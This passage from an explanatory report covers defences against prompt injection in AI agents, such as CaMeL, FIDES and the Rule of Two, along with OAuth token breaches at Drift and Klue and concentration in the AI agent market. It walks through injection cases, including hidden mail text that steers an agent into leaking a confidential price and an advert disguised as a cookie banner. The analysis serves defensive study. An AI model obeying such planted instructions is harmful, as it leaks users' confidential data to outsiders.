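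Model-written rules are safest when the model has seen only trusted text. *Authority Is Not a String* (2026) applies this to a coding agent by having software limit the agent's permissions for the whole task before it reads any files or tool output. When the agent starts a sub-agent, it proposes the sub-agent's permissions, which cannot exceed that limit. *Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation* (2026) also fixes a plan in advance. Ordinary code compares each call with the plan, and a reasoning model examines only the calls that do not fit. The drawback of both designs is that an agent often learns what access it needs only partway through the task.

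The user's request may not be trustworthy either. Shi and colleagues assume that it is, but people paste emails and web pages into their requests. If the sales employee pasted in the customer's message, hidden text in it could reach the policy model before any policy existed. Progent's solver could not detect the problem, because it only compares a new policy with an earlier one. Surapani and colleagues raise a similar concern about PAuth, that a manipulated request could lead a service to expect a broader call than the user intended. MiniScope treats the user's instructions as trusted, but not everything in the request, and relies on the user to notice an unexpected permission prompt.

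Progent can also have a person review the first policy and every expansion. No attack in AgentDojo succeeded with this setting, but Shi and colleagues assumed a reviewer with strong security awareness who would never approve a malicious recipient. In contrast, most of Anthropic's paid testers approved a clearly dangerous command.

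## Does tracking where data goes prevent harm that permissions allow?

Tracking data can stop an agent from misusing permissions that its task needs. The sales agent has to read the customer's mail and send mail, so its owner cannot take away either permission. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) notes that a valid credential does not establish which specific actions someone has authorised. In tests, agents that track data blocked nearly all injected instructions, but they also failed at many legitimate tasks, especially those whose steps depend on what the agent reads.

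Suppose the employee also asks the agent to confirm the meeting time with the customer. The agent now needs to open the customer's record, which includes the lowest price the company would accept, and to write to the customer. The customer's mail thread contains a hidden instruction to add that price to the confirmation. The agent needs all of these permissions for the task, and a rule limiting recipients would allow the message because the customer is a permitted recipient. Software can block the message only if it keeps track of the fact that the price came from a record the customer isn't allowed to see.

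### Labels for secrecy and trust

Information-flow control attaches labels to data, carries them along whenever software copies or combines the data, and checks them before the agent acts. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, use two kinds of label. A confidentiality label lists who may read an item, and an integrity label records whether the item is trusted. An item is untrusted if an outsider could have written it. The sales agent's data might have these labels:

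| Item | Who may read it | Trusted? |
|---|---|---|
| The employee's request | Anyone | Yes |
| Meeting time, from the employee's calendar | Sales team and customer | Yes |
| Customer's mail thread | Sales team and customer | No |
| Customer's record, with the lowest price | Sales team | Yes |
| Finished brief, made from all of these | Sales team | No |

The last row follows from the others. Only people who may read every ingredient may read the result, and one untrusted ingredient makes the result untrusted. If R(x) is the set of people who may read item x, then

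R(x combined with y) = R(x) ∩ R(y)

Before the agent sends message m to a set of recipients P, the software checks that

P ⊆ R(m)

and that only trusted data influenced the decision to send m and the choice of recipients. A confirmation that includes the lowest price fails the check on readers, because the customer is not on the sales team. A confirmation with only the meeting time passes. The brief may go to the colleague, who is on the sales team, even though its text is partly untrusted. A stricter policy that Costa and colleagues also describe would require the text to be trusted too, which would rule out any brief that summarises a customer's mail.

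The check on readers limits what an attacker can steal, but an attacker could still trigger messages that reveal nothing secret. The check on trust stops outsiders from triggering messages, but on its own it would let the employee send the price to the customer by mistake.

Costa and colleagues show that their method can guarantee "explicit secrecy", meaning that confidential data cannot flow directly to someone not permitted to read it. The guarantee does not cover what an outsider can infer from the agent's behaviour. For example, if the agent writes only to customers whose records mark them as likely to cancel, a customer who receives a message can infer how they were marked. Once the agent might have read something confidential, preventing such inferences would mean blocking almost every action outsiders can see, which Costa and colleagues consider too restrictive.

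The guarantee also depends on correct labels. In *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026) found that none of the systems they surveyed adequately specifies how to assign labels. They warn that Microsoft's system treats data as trusted if a developer forgets to label it. Their company, LaunchSafe, builds security tools for agents, but this weakness is easy to see in the designs.

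Language models also make tracking harder, because software usually cannot determine which of the texts a model has read influenced its answer. The software therefore gives the answer the strictest labels among those texts. Once an ordinary agent has read the customer's thread, its next decision counts as untrusted and it cannot send the brief. CaMeL and FIDES avoid this by keeping untrusted text away from the model that chooses the actions.

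### CaMeL: a plan fixed in advance

Researchers at Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich introduced CaMeL in 2025. It develops an idea of Willison's from 2023, in which two models divide the work. One model sees the user's request but no outside text, and writes a program for the whole task. The other reads outside text but cannot call tools. For the original sales brief, the program might look like this, with invented functions:

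```
event  = read_calendar("2026-10-08")
thread = find_latest_thread("Northgate")
record = read_record("Northgate")
brief  = ask_isolated_model("Write a one-page brief",
                            [event, thread, record])
send_mail(to="colleague@company.example", body=brief)
```

Ordinary software runs the program, tracks where each value came from and who may read it, and checks these labels before each tool call. Suppose hidden text in the thread contains an instruction to send the customer's record to an outsider. Only the isolated model reads that text, and it can only return the text of the brief. The program already contains the recipient's address, and nothing in the thread can add another `send_mail` line.

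The hidden text could still make the isolated model write the false 40% discount into the brief. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) explains that a fixed plan protects the choice and order of actions, but not the data that passes through them. CaMeL's label checks can stop some harmful data from reaching a tool, but its designers say they do not aim to prevent attacks that only change text. They also demonstrated two ways an attacker could learn private information indirectly, including by causing an error while the program runs.

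According to Narisetty and colleagues, an agent based on OpenAI's o3 completed 77% of AgentDojo's tasks with CaMeL and 84% without it. None of the attacks that CaMeL is meant to stop succeeded. With CaMeL, the models processed about 2.8 times as much text and wrote about 2.7 times as much as without it.

### FIDES: one step at a time

Some tasks don't fit a plan written in advance. For example, an agent asked to check three emails for a meeting request and add any meeting to the calendar cannot know whether it will need the calendar until it has the emails. FIDES, the system that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, lets the planning model choose each step after the previous one finishes.

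1. The planning model calls the mail tool. The software stores the untrusted text of the emails in a variable, and the planning model sees only the variable's name.
2. The planning model asks an isolated model whether the emails contain a meeting request. The software forces the answer to be either true or false.
3. The planning model reads the answer. If it is true, the isolated model extracts the date, time and participants into another variable.
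4. The planning model passes that variable to the calendar tool without reading it.

The true-or-false answer is still untrusted, so a strict policy would block the calendar entry. FIDES can relax the policy for such answers because one bit is too small to hold an instruction, but an attacker could still put a false meeting in the calendar. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby et al., 2026) notes that these systems often weaken their guarantees to stay usable, and that reviewers should examine those exceptions most closely.

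Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o, without the true-or-false feature, which they judged unnecessary for most of the benchmark's tasks. The table shows how many attacks succeeded, counted after they reviewed the results by hand, and the share of tasks that agents completed when there was no attack.

| Design | Successful attacks | Office work | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
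| Ordinary agent | 152 | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary agent with label checks | 0 | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES without label checks | 21 | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% |
| FIDES with label checks | 0 | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

Costa and colleagues emphasise that FIDES completed 8 percentage points more tasks on average than an ordinary agent with the same checks. But most companies would be comparing it with an ordinary agent that has no checks, which completed an average of 84% of tasks across the four areas, while FIDES completed 50%. FIDES does better with a stronger model, completing 68% of the travel tasks with OpenAI's o1. CaMeL's smaller loss was measured with a different model, so the two results don't show which design is better.

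Many of the failures were by design. Several banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, and FIDES blocks the payment because an outsider could have written the file. In another task, the user asked the agent to change the password if the account showed a suspicious transaction. The agent changed it without reading the untrusted transaction descriptions, because it judged a large amount to be suspicious. This broke no rule, although a large payment is weak evidence of fraud.

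There are also two reasons to be cautious about the zeros in the table. AgentDojo's own scoring counted three successful attacks against FIDES with label checks, but in their review the researchers did not count attempts that the software had blocked, actions that their policies allowed, or attacks that only changed text. They had also labelled as untrusted every data field that the benchmark's attacks use, whereas a company would have to label its data without knowing where attacks will come from.

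### Adaptive attackers and open-ended tasks

A defence that stops a fixed list of attacks can still fail against an attacker who adapts to the defence. Narisetty and colleagues cite a study in which Milad Nasr and others tested twelve defences, mostly filters and specially trained models. Most had been reported to stop nearly all attacks, but adaptive attacks succeeded against most of them more than 90% of the time.

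CaMeL has held up much better. In *AutoDojo*, Ma, Li and colleagues (2026) tested ten defences against an attacker that rewrites its planted text up to six times, knowing only whether each version worked. The five main models included GPT-5.4-mini and DeepSeek-v4-Flash. CaMeL was the most effective defence overall. Rewording an instruction does not change the label on the text, but it can fool a filter. Attacks on one filter, PIGuard, went from never succeeding to succeeding 28% of the time when the agent used GPT-4o-mini.

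CaMeL also reduced task completion the most on four of the five models, by more than PIGuard and another filter, which cut it by a quarter to a half. ROPE, a newer system that also tracks where data comes from, reduced task completion by at most 7 percentage points in the main tests, so large losses may not be inevitable. However, some of the same researchers developed both ROPE and AutoDojo.

Open-ended tasks are a more serious problem for CaMeL. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) includes 60 tasks in which the agent has to change its plan along the way, for instance because a checkout page requires it to log in first. An undefended agent based on GPT-4o completed 53% of them. With CaMeL, agents based on GPT-4o, Gemini 2.5 Pro, Claude 3.5 Sonnet and Llama 3.3 70B completed none. No attacks succeeded against the CaMeL agents either, but that means little when they could not complete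 any tasks. Progent, the rule-based system described earlier, completed only 6.7% of the tasks with GPT-4o.

This weakness is hard to see in AgentDojo because only 6 of its 97 tasks require a change of plan, whereas all of AgentDyn's do. Ordinary work probably falls in between. A fixed plan suits the sales brief but not "deal with whatever the customer asks for in her last email", because the email has to determine the actions. CaMeL usually asks the user to approve such actions, which brings back the problem of people approving prompts without reading them.

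Setting up CaMeL for a new environment also takes work. *Evolution Under Fire* (2026) left it out of one of two benchmarks because CaMeL's policies are specific to each benchmark and its program runner could not work with the generic test setup.

Labels must also outlast a single request. If the agent saves the brief today and reads it again next week, hidden text from the customer could take effect then, unless the saved file is still marked as untrusted. *SPA* (2026) proposes a system that keeps labels on saved data and plans each new request without showing that data to the planning model. The paper adapts AgentDojo to include delayed attacks like this one, and finds that strong protection again reduced the number of tasks completed.

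### The Rule of Two as a shortcut

Meta's Agents Rule of Two is a coarser approach to the same problem. It applies to a whole session instead of each item of data, so a developer can use it without labels or a special interpreter. The developer only has to check that an unsupervised agent does not combine all three of the rule's properties: untrustworthy inputs, sensitive access, and the ability to change things or communicate externally.

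Meta illustrates the rule with an imaginary Email-Bot that summarises an inbox and sends replies. Its developer could let it read mail only from trusted senders, deny it access to private data, or require a person to check any draft to someone who isn't a trusted recipient. The last option would suit the sales brief, since the colleague could be a trusted recipient.

An agent may also change which two properties it has during a session. The sales agent could search the public web for news about the customer, then permanently lose the ability to communicate before it opens the customer's record. Hidden text from the web could not make the agent send the record out, though it could still distort the brief. The employee would have to send the brief herself.

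The company Evoke Security (2025) objects that keeping an agent away from private data limits what it can do, and that relying on human approval shifts the burden to users, who are known to fail at it. The experiment in which most of Anthropic's testers approved a dangerous command supports the second objection. Meta had already conceded in its original post that a user might blindly confirm a warning and that some background work is hard to fit into the rule, which it presents as a supplement to least privilege. But Meta's diagram labelled every pair of properties "Safe", a stronger claim than the text supports.

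### Agents that operate a screen

CaMeL and FIDES need tools with a clear meaning. Software can check the recipient in a call such as `send_mail(to, body)`, but a call such as `click(412, 230)` might open a message, delete it or pay a bill, depending on what is on the screen. The agent also has to look at the screen to know where to click, and the screen often shows the application's own buttons next to text from strangers.

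Foerster and colleagues, some of whom helped develop CaMeL, adapted it to these agents. The planning model has no access to the screen, so it writes a long program with branches for the situations the agent might meet. During the task, an isolated model answers narrow questions about the screen, such as whether a cookie banner is visible or where the "Save" button is, and the program follows the matching branch. These programs averaged 213 lines, compared with 52 for CaMeL on AgentDojo, and roughly half the steps were fallbacks that never ran.

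The design was tested on OSWorld, a benchmark of tasks in browsers, office software and other desktop programs. Of 109 tasks that Claude Sonnet 4.5 could complete without the separation, it completed 57% with the separation when given five attempts, and 28% when given one. The higher figure depends on someone being able to pick out the successful attempt, which is harder if a failed one has already sent an email or deleted a file.

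With a smaller model operating the screen, the design used 1.88 times as much text as an undefended agent. A version based on FIDES used 29.6 times as much, because it sent the whole history back to the planning model at every step.

An attacker cannot add new actions to such a plan, but can trick the agent into taking the wrong branch. Foerster and colleagues call this "branch steering". In their demonstration, an advertisement was made to look like a cookie banner. The plan included dealing with cookie banners, so the agent clicked the advertisement and went to the attacker's site. The researchers tried checking the screen against the web page's code and using a second model to confirm the first model's reading of the screen. Both checks failed against some versions of the attack. They did not use CaMeL's label rules here, because those rules can be applied to an action only when its effect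 is known.

Another approach checks the effect of a click instead of the click itself. Christodorescu and colleagues describe ceLLMate, which examines the messages a browser sends to a website. Posting a comment and deleting an issue produce different messages, whichever button the agent clicks, so a rule can allow one and block the other. The rules rely on information from the website's developers, and automatically turning a user's request into rules remains an open problem. Foerster and colleagues add that the method is hard to apply to desktop programs, where clicks may produce no web traffic to inspect.

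### Why agents still need narrow permissions

Christodorescu and colleagues argue that strengthening one part of a system is rarely enough, and that designers should put fixed checks at several layers. At least four of the 11 attacks on real agents that they examine, including one on Microsoft Copilot, violated both least privilege (the agent had more access than it should have had) and secure information flow (data went where it should not have gone).

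Narrow permissions limit the damage when a label is wrong. If someone marked the customer's thread as trusted by mistake, hidden text could direct the agent, but a token for one thread and one recipient would still restrict what the agent could read and where it could send data. Permissions also protect against mistakes that labels would not stop because no untrusted text is involved, such as the deletion of PocketOS's database.

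## What happens when one company holds the access tokens of many customers?

When one company stores the access tokens of many customers, a single break-in can expose all of those customers' data within days. Policy layers and data labels don't help, because they restrict the agent, and a thief who copies tokens from the company's servers can use them without going through the agent. This happened in August 2025 to customers of Drift, an AI chat agent that companies put on their websites, mainly for sales.

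### The Drift breach

Companies typically connect Drift to other systems to track their dealings with customers, and The Record notes that these include Salesforce's. Drift therefore held OAuth tokens for its customers' Salesforce accounts, and some customers also connected a mailbox or Slack. Cloudflare (2025), an internet infrastructure and security company, used Drift so that visitors to its website could contact it. Anyone holding Cloudflare's Drift token could also read the text of its support cases, access that a contact form does not obviously need.

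The theft began at Salesloft, the company that owns Drift. According to Salesloft's *Trust Center*, an intruder had access to its GitHub account from March to June 2025, downloaded code and added a guest user. The intruder then got into Drift's servers at Amazon Web Services (AWS) and took the customers' tokens. CyberScoop's *Security leaders at Okta and Zscaler share lessons from Salesloft Drift attacks* notes that Salesloft did not explain how the intruder entered either system. Salesloft's final summary adds that the intruder searched its code for secrets and copied some. The intruder may have used one of these to get into the AWS account, but Salesloft does not confirm this.

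Google threat researchers Larsen, Lin and colleagues (2025) report in *Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift* that the intruder exported large amounts of data from Salesforce customers between 8 and 18 August, including support cases and records of accounts, users and sales opportunities. The intruder then searched the data for passwords, AWS keys and access tokens for the data-storage service Snowflake, so a token for a company's sales records could also lead to access to its servers.

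Salesloft at first said the incident affected only customers who had connected Drift to Salesforce. On 28 August, Larsen and colleagues reported that the intruder had also used tokens from Drift's email product to open a very small number of Google Workspace mailboxes. They told every Drift customer to treat all tokens stored with Drift as potentially compromised. The software company Elastic found that its Salesforce data was safe but one of its email accounts was exposed.

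Google told The Hacker News (2025) that it knew of over 700 "potentially impacted" organisations, a figure usually reported as the number of victims. The thief also targeted the identity company Okta but failed to get in. When CyberScoop published its article, nearly 40 companies had publicly said the attack affected them. The number of organisations that lost data is probably between these two figures.

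Cloudflare used logs to reconstruct how the intruder stole its data. The intruder first logged in on 12 August, then spent several days counting records and finding out how many requests Salesforce would accept. On 17 August, the intruder copied the text of the support cases in just over three minutes, then tried to hide the theft by deleting the export job. Salesloft and Salesforce revoked all of Drift's tokens on 20 August, but Cloudflare did not learn that it was a victim until 23 August. In the stolen text, it found 104 Cloudflare access tokens that customers had pasted into support requests. It replaced them all and saw no sign that anyone had used them.

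According to Konthalapally's *When OAuth Tokens Go Rogue*, the stolen tokens completely bypassed multi-factor login, which asks for a second proof such as a code from a phone. Salesforce asks for that proof when a person signs in, and Drift's customers had already signed in when they approved the connection. The thief used the tokens created by that approval, so there was no new sign-in to check. Microsoft (2026) found that attacks of this kind copy sales records in bulk without causing the usual warning signs at login.

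None of these accounts suggests that anyone misled Drift's chat agent. Any product that stored tokens in the same way could have lost them.

### Klue, ten months later

Klue, a market intelligence company, had connections to its customers' Salesforce accounts. On 11 June 2026, an intruder used a stolen GitHub token to insert code into the service that manages these connections, and the code collected access and refresh tokens. According to Klue's *CrowdStrike Investigation Summary* (2026), Salesforce noticed suspicious activity the next day and warned Klue, which shut down the affected systems that morning.

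The accounts of how the intruder got in don't quite match. The Hacker News (2026) reported that Klue first told customers the intruder had used an old credential belonging to an integration service. Huntress, a security company that lost data, described a credential left over from an abandoned prototype, according to Help Net Security's *Klue breach lead to Salesforce data theft, Huntress affected* (2026). CrowdStrike, which investigated for Klue, identified a GitHub token but could not determine how the intruder had obtained it. All three may be describing the same credential.

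Attackers stole data from Klue's customers despite Klue's quick response. They took business contacts, price quotes and sales messages from Huntress. Datadog's *Detecting the Klue supply chain attack in Salesforce instances* (2026) reports that extortion emails with a 48-hour deadline began to arrive on 16 June.

Between these two cases, intruders stole tokens from Gainsight, which makes software for managing customer relationships. Okta's *First Drift, now Gainsight* (2025) reports that the breach exposed the tokens of more than 200 organisations. In all, three suppliers lost Salesforce tokens within ten months.

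### How common are these connections?

Companies that make AI models now hold such tokens too. Nudge Security, which sells software for tracking employees' use of AI tools, found OpenAI products in 96.9% of the organisations it observed and Anthropic products in 94.5%. Of these organisations, 67% had at least one OpenAI integration and 74% had at least one Anthropic integration, according to Help Net Security's *AI agents inherit employee access, and nobody’s watching how they use it*. At least 41% therefore had both. Most of the integrations were OAuth grants that employees had approved, and the most common connection was to Google Workspace.

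The sample consists of Nudge's customers, who have chosen to monitor their AI tools and may not resemble other companies. An organisation counts even if only one employee has connected one mailbox. These providers hold tokens from most of the sample, but the figures don't measure how much data those tokens cover.

Nudge also found that agents often run on the credentials of the employee who created them, and may keep that access after the employee changes roles. Access grants stay in place until someone revokes them, often long after the employee has stopped using the tool. The coverage gives no percentages for either pattern.

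Many smaller companies are involved as well. Nudge counted 2,927 AI vendors across its customers, and twelve tools from companies other than OpenAI and Anthropic each appeared in more than half of the organisations.

### The arithmetic of pooled access

If 700 firms each keep their own tokens and each has an independent chance p of a breach in a given year, the expected number of breached firms is 700p. If one supplier holds all 700 firms' tokens and has the same chance p of a breach, the expected number is still 700p, but the firms all lose their tokens together. The table shows the result when p is 1%.

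| | 700 firms with their own tokens | One supplier with all 700 tokens |
|---|---|---|
| Expected number of breached firms | 7 | 7 |
| Chance of no breach at all | 0.09% | 99% |
| Chance that all 700 firms are breached | Practically zero | 1% |
| Standard deviation | 2.6 firms | 70 firms |

When one company holds many customers' access tokens, nearly every year passes without a breach, whereas a few firms would be breached every year if each stored its own. Customers may therefore conclude from experience that pooled storage is safe.

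Losing everything at once also causes harm that the expected number doesn't measure. Hundreds of firms need investigators in the same week, and secrets stolen from one can help the thief attack another. Three days before first logging in at Cloudflare, the intruder tried a token that Cloudflare had issued to a customer. The token may have come from an earlier Drift victim. But a shared supplier can also shut the thief out everywhere with one action, as Salesloft did on 20 August.

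The supplier's chance of a breach, q, probably differs from p. Pooling reduces the expected number of breached firms only if q is lower than p. If q is 0.5%, the expected number falls from 7 to 3.5, and if q is 2%, it rises to 14.

A larger prize probably raises q. The intruder was in Salesloft's systems for months before using the stolen tokens, which would be a lot of effort for one firm's sales records. Once a thief has the tokens, attacking each additional customer takes very little extra work. David Bradbury, Okta's chief security officer, told CyberScoop that his working hypothesis was that a single script attacked all the customers at once.

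A specialist may also defend tokens better than its customers would. A supplier with hundreds of clients can pay for a security team, while a small firm may leave a working token in an ordinary file, as happened at PocketOS. But customers have trouble telling a careful supplier from a careless one. Zscaler's security chief, Sam Curry, said that Salesloft had passed Zscaler's security questionnaire and probably hundreds of others. The three breaches don't show whether q is usually above or below p, since suppliers that protect their tokens well don't make the news.

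The comparison is also kinder to pooling than real life is, because a supplier's risk usually comes on top of the firm's own. A thief can still attack the firm's Salesforce account directly. And a firm rarely has only one supplier. With twelve, each with an independent 1% chance of a breach, the chance that at least one loses the firm's tokens in a year is

1 − 0.99¹² ≈ 11%

### Which remedies would have stopped the theft?

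| Remedy | Would it have stopped the Drift theft? |
|---|---|
| Accept a token only from the supplier's network addresses | Yes, and it did at Okta |
| Bind each token to a private key | Probably, unless the intruder could also use the key |
| Keep the tokens on the customer's own systems | Probably, though an intruder might still have sent requests through Drift |
| Monitor how connections are used | Only if someone had acted on the early signs |
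| Make access tokens expire quickly | No |
| End unused grants automatically | Only for customers who had stopped using Drift |

Only the first measure has direct evidence from the attack itself. Okta had set Salesforce to accept its Drift token only from approved network addresses. Okta's *The Salesloft incident* (2025) reports that the thief tried the token from elsewhere and failed. Drift had published its addresses before the attack, so other customers could have set the same limit. Few did, because it can take days or weeks of testing, and many applications other than Salesforce don't offer it. The limit would probably have worked at Klue too, since Datadog lists outside addresses that the thief used. It would fail against an intruder who sent requests from the supplier's own servers.

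Bradbury argues that DPoP, the OAuth extension that ties a token to a private key, would have prevented the Drift theft. Okta sells products that support DPoP, but the reasoning is sound if the intruder could copy the tokens but not the keys. Salesloft has not said how Drift stored its tokens, so outsiders can't tell whether the keys would have been safer. DPoP might have helped less at Klue, because the intruder's code ran inside the service that managed the connections and might have been able to use the keys there.

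If customers kept the tokens themselves, a break-in at the supplier would not expose 700 of them. Oasis Security's *The Salesloft OAuth compromise* advertises a product that stores secrets inside the customer's own systems, though this is a vendor's claim. Each customer would have to run and protect that storage, which brings back 700 separate chances of a breach. The supplier would also still need a way to request data, which an intruder could misuse for as long as the break-in lasted.

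Some Drift customers managed their own connections through API keys, but Drift also held copies of those keys. Salesloft could cancel the OAuth tokens centrally, but these customers had to revoke their API keys themselves in each connected application.

Monitoring had a fair chance of catching the thief at Cloudflare, where almost five days passed between the first login and the export. The thief used unfamiliar addresses and a program that identified itself as "Salesforce-Multi-Org-Fetcher". In the Klue attack, Datadog, which sells monitoring software, found bursts of failed requests for far more data than Salesforce would return. But Microsoft says that the activity in the Gainsight attack often looked the same as normal use of a legitimate connection. An alert also has to lead to action quickly. Salesforce raised the alarm about Klue within about a day, but Huntress's data had already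 been taken.

Short-lived access tokens would have made little difference, because the Drift thief also had refresh tokens and needed only three minutes to copy Cloudflare's cases. In the Klue attack, Datadog saw refresh tokens in use at only some of the victims, so access tokens were apparently enough at the others. Cloudflare now replaces the secrets for its connected services every week. That shortens the useful life of a stolen secret, but the Drift thief went from first login to export in less than a week.

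Zscaler had stopped using Drift in July, for reasons unrelated to security, but left the token active until the end of August to make sure nothing still depended on it. A rule that automatically ended grants two weeks after their last use might have closed the connection before the theft, though Google's limit of six months without use would not have. An expiry rule also has to count only use by people, because software that copies data automatically every night can keep a forgotten grant active for years.

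## How concentrated is the market for AI agents, and does access to data make it more so?

The market for AI agents is highly concentrated by the usual measure, although shares are changing quickly. OpenAI, Anthropic and Google serve most of the people who use agents. Most of the organisations that Nudge Security observed have connected at least one application to OpenAI, and most have connected at least one to Anthropic. It is unclear how much of the leaders' advantage comes from access to users' data.

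### What the 84% counts

OpenAI, Google and Anthropic together held over 84% of the worldwide AI agent sector in May 2026, according to *Avis n° 26-A-05 du 17 juillet 2026* (2026), an advisory opinion by France's competition authority, the Autorité de la concurrence. The authority opened its inquiry on its own initiative in January 2026 and received about 40 contributions from companies and institutions. The opinion contains no accusations of lawbreaking.

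The authority defines the sector broadly, using "AI agent" both for assistants that only converse and for systems that act through tools. Someone who asks ChatGPT for a recipe counts as a user just as much as a sales employee whose agent can open her mailbox. The authority did not examine how agents relate to search engines. It only had to describe a sector, so it did not have to determine which products customers accept as substitutes, as it normally would in a merger case.

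The opinion gives the 84% without stating whether it counts users, visits or revenue. The authority took the figure from an article on the news site 01net, which used data from the research company Sensor Tower. It probably counts users, because Sensor Tower's *State of AI 2026 Report* (2026) measures share by unique users across mobile apps and the web. According to EMARKETER's *ChatGPT's market share decline marks AI's shift from models to distribution*, Sensor Tower's shares for May were 46.4% for ChatGPT, 27.7% for Google's Gemini and 10.3% for Anthropic's Claude, which add up to 84.4%.

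Other measures change the ranking. By time spent in assistant apps in early 2026, Sensor Tower ranks ChatGPT, Gemini and the Chinese assistant DeepSeek highest, with nearly 90% of that time between them. Claude drops out of the top three, possibly because its users are mostly on the web. Among Nudge's customers, more organisations had connected Anthropic than OpenAI. Nudge's count bears more directly on who holds access, though its sample is much narrower.

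User counts also don't measure how much people use each product. Huang (2026), in *State of AI 2026*, puts average use at about 215 minutes a month for ChatGPT, 120 for Claude and 100 for Gemini. Weighting the May shares by these minutes gives ChatGPT about 71% of the time people spend on the three, compared with 55% of their users. This is a rough estimate, since the minutes and the shares may not cover the same products and months.

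### The concentration index

Competition authorities usually measure concentration with the Herfindahl–Hirschman index (HHI), which adds up the squares of all firms' market shares in percent:

HHI = s₁² + s₂² + s₃² + …

The Herfindahl-Hirschman index adds up the squares of firms' percentage market shares, so a monopoly scores 100² = 10,000 and a market of a hundred equal firms scores 100. Squaring gives large firms more weight, so one firm with a 40% share adds twice as much to the index as two firms with 20% each.

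If three firms hold 84% of the market, they contribute at least 3 × 28² = 2,352 points to the Herfindahl-Hirschman index, the sum of squared market shares. That minimum assumes an equal split. The actual split is unequal, so their total is higher, at about 3,026 points. ChatGPT contributes 46.4² ≈ 2,153, Gemini 767 and Claude 106. The remaining 15.6% of the market can add at most 243 points, which would require a single firm to hold all of it.

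| | Points |
|---|---|
| Line for "highly concentrated" in the US merger guidelines of 2023 | 1,800 |
| Upper line in the European Commission's 2004 guidelines on mergers between competitors | 2,000 |
| Three equal firms with 84%, ignoring the rest | 2,352 |
| AI agents in May 2026, by users | 3,026 to 3,270 |

The market is well above both thresholds, however the small firms divide the remaining share. But authorities use these thresholds to decide which mergers to examine, and a high score is not an offence. Under the US guidelines, authorities presume a merger is harmful if it leaves the market above 1,800 points and raises the index by more than 100. If Google bought an agent maker with a 2% share, the index would rise by 2 × 27.7 × 2 ≈ 111 points, enough to trigger that presumption.

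The index describes the market at one moment, so it doesn't show whether the leader is secure or losing ground. This makes it less informative in a young market. Sensor Tower projected that people would spend 36 billion hours on generative AI apps in the first half of 2026, up from 17.2 billion a year earlier. Many future customers have therefore not chosen an agent yet, or have only just started using one. ChatGPT's share has fallen steadily since September 2025 and dropped below half for the first time in March 2026.

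The index can also understate concentration, because it treats firms as independent even when some rely on others' models. Perplexity builds its assistant on models from companies such as OpenAI and Anthropic, and Apple has agreed to use Google's Gemini models for its new version of Siri. If all iPhone users switched from ChatGPT to Siri, the index might fall while Google's influence grew.

### Why it is easier to start than to grow

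A company can launch an agent without training a model. It can pay to use another company's model through a programming interface, or run an "open-weight" model, whose developer has published the trained parameters. The Autorité de la concurrence found over 100 models on Amazon's marketplace and over 200 on Google's. Amazon and Apple use outside models for some products, though they could probably afford to train their own.

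This route leaves the newcomer dependent on its supplier, which controls the model's price, performance and updates and may sell a competing agent. Some suppliers also forbid customers from using the model's output to develop rival models. In June 2026, the US government ordered Anthropic to block foreign nationals from using its Fable 5 and Mythos 5 models, then lifted the restriction a few weeks later. Open-weight models avoid much of this dependence, but they require more technical skill, and the authority doubts that they will always be good enough to compete.

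Growth is harder, mainly because a new agent has to reach users who already have another one on their phone or in their office software. The authority also lists access to data, the difficulty of switching between agents, and the cost of running them as obstacles. It cites an estimate by the consultancy EY that a chatbot's response cost 4 US cents in 2023, while a complex task that an agent organises costs $1.20 on average in 2026. At that price, a newcomer with a million users who each set ten such tasks a month would spend $12 million a month.

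Running costs explain less of the market's concentration than they seem to. In ordinary software, serving one more customer costs almost nothing, so the largest seller has a much lower cost per user. A large agent maker has less of this advantage because its running costs rise with use. These costs mainly favour companies that can fund years of losses or, like Google, own the chips and data centres.

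### How access could feed concentration

The four advantages below could reinforce one another. Suppose the sales employee's company uses an office suite whose maker also sells an agent.

1. The agent is already in her mail program, so she tries it before any other.
2. It can use her mail and calendar at once, while a rival needs her consent and has to satisfy the suite maker's conditions for access.
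3. Her corrections show the provider which answers worked. If its terms allow, the provider uses them to improve the agent for everyone.
4. The agent stores what it has learned about her customers and how she likes her briefs. Each month, a new agent would have more to catch up on.

A better agent then attracts more users, and application makers have more reason to support it. Economists call this a network effect, meaning that a product becomes more valuable to each user as others join. These steps are plausible, but their effect could be small, and the summary of the French opinion does not estimate how much any of them raises a firm's market share.

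The evidence that default placement helps AI agents gain users is mixed. Huang links Gemini's growth in Europe, the United States, Japan and South Korea to its integration with Android and Google's other services, but this is an interpretation, since nobody compared similar users with and without the integration. Claude had no phone or office suite of its own, yet its audience grew by 452% in the year to May 2026. Microsoft's Copilot is prominent in Office but is not among the three leaders. This is only weak evidence that default placement doesn't help, because a count of app and web users may miss people who use Copilot inside Word.

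Data from a firm's other services can help its agent do a task for a particular user and help the firm improve its product for everyone, and these two advantages call for different remedies. An agent preparing a sales brief for an employee needs her mail, which a rival can get through a connector if she agrees. Improving the product benefits from patterns across millions of people, which no single user can hand over. In *AI agents*, the press release on its opinion, the Autorité de la concurrence argues that competitors cannot reasonably replicate the large firms' data, but it considers the barrier lower for specialised agents. A legal research agent, for example, may gain more from a law firm's own files than from the general public's questions.

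How much a firm gains from learning from its users depends on how quickly the benefit of each additional user shrinks. Suppose, for illustration, that every doubling of users improves an agent by the same amount. ChatGPT has about 4.5 times as many users as Claude, or a little over two doublings, so Anthropic could make up the difference with a somewhat better model. If quality instead rose in direct proportion to users, Claude would have had little chance of growing as it did. Its growth suggests that the advantage of having more users was not overwhelming in 2026, at least for the tasks Claude's users cared about.

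The history an agent stores becomes more valuable the longer someone uses the agent. A person who only asks questions may be able to change agents in a minute, but a sales employee would lose the agent's notes on her customers and have to set up access again. The Autorité de la concurrence therefore warns of lock-in, in which customers stay because leaving is difficult. Lock-in would grow as chatbots become agents, so how easily people switch chatbots today may be a poor guide to how they will behave later.

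### The case that agents make markets more open

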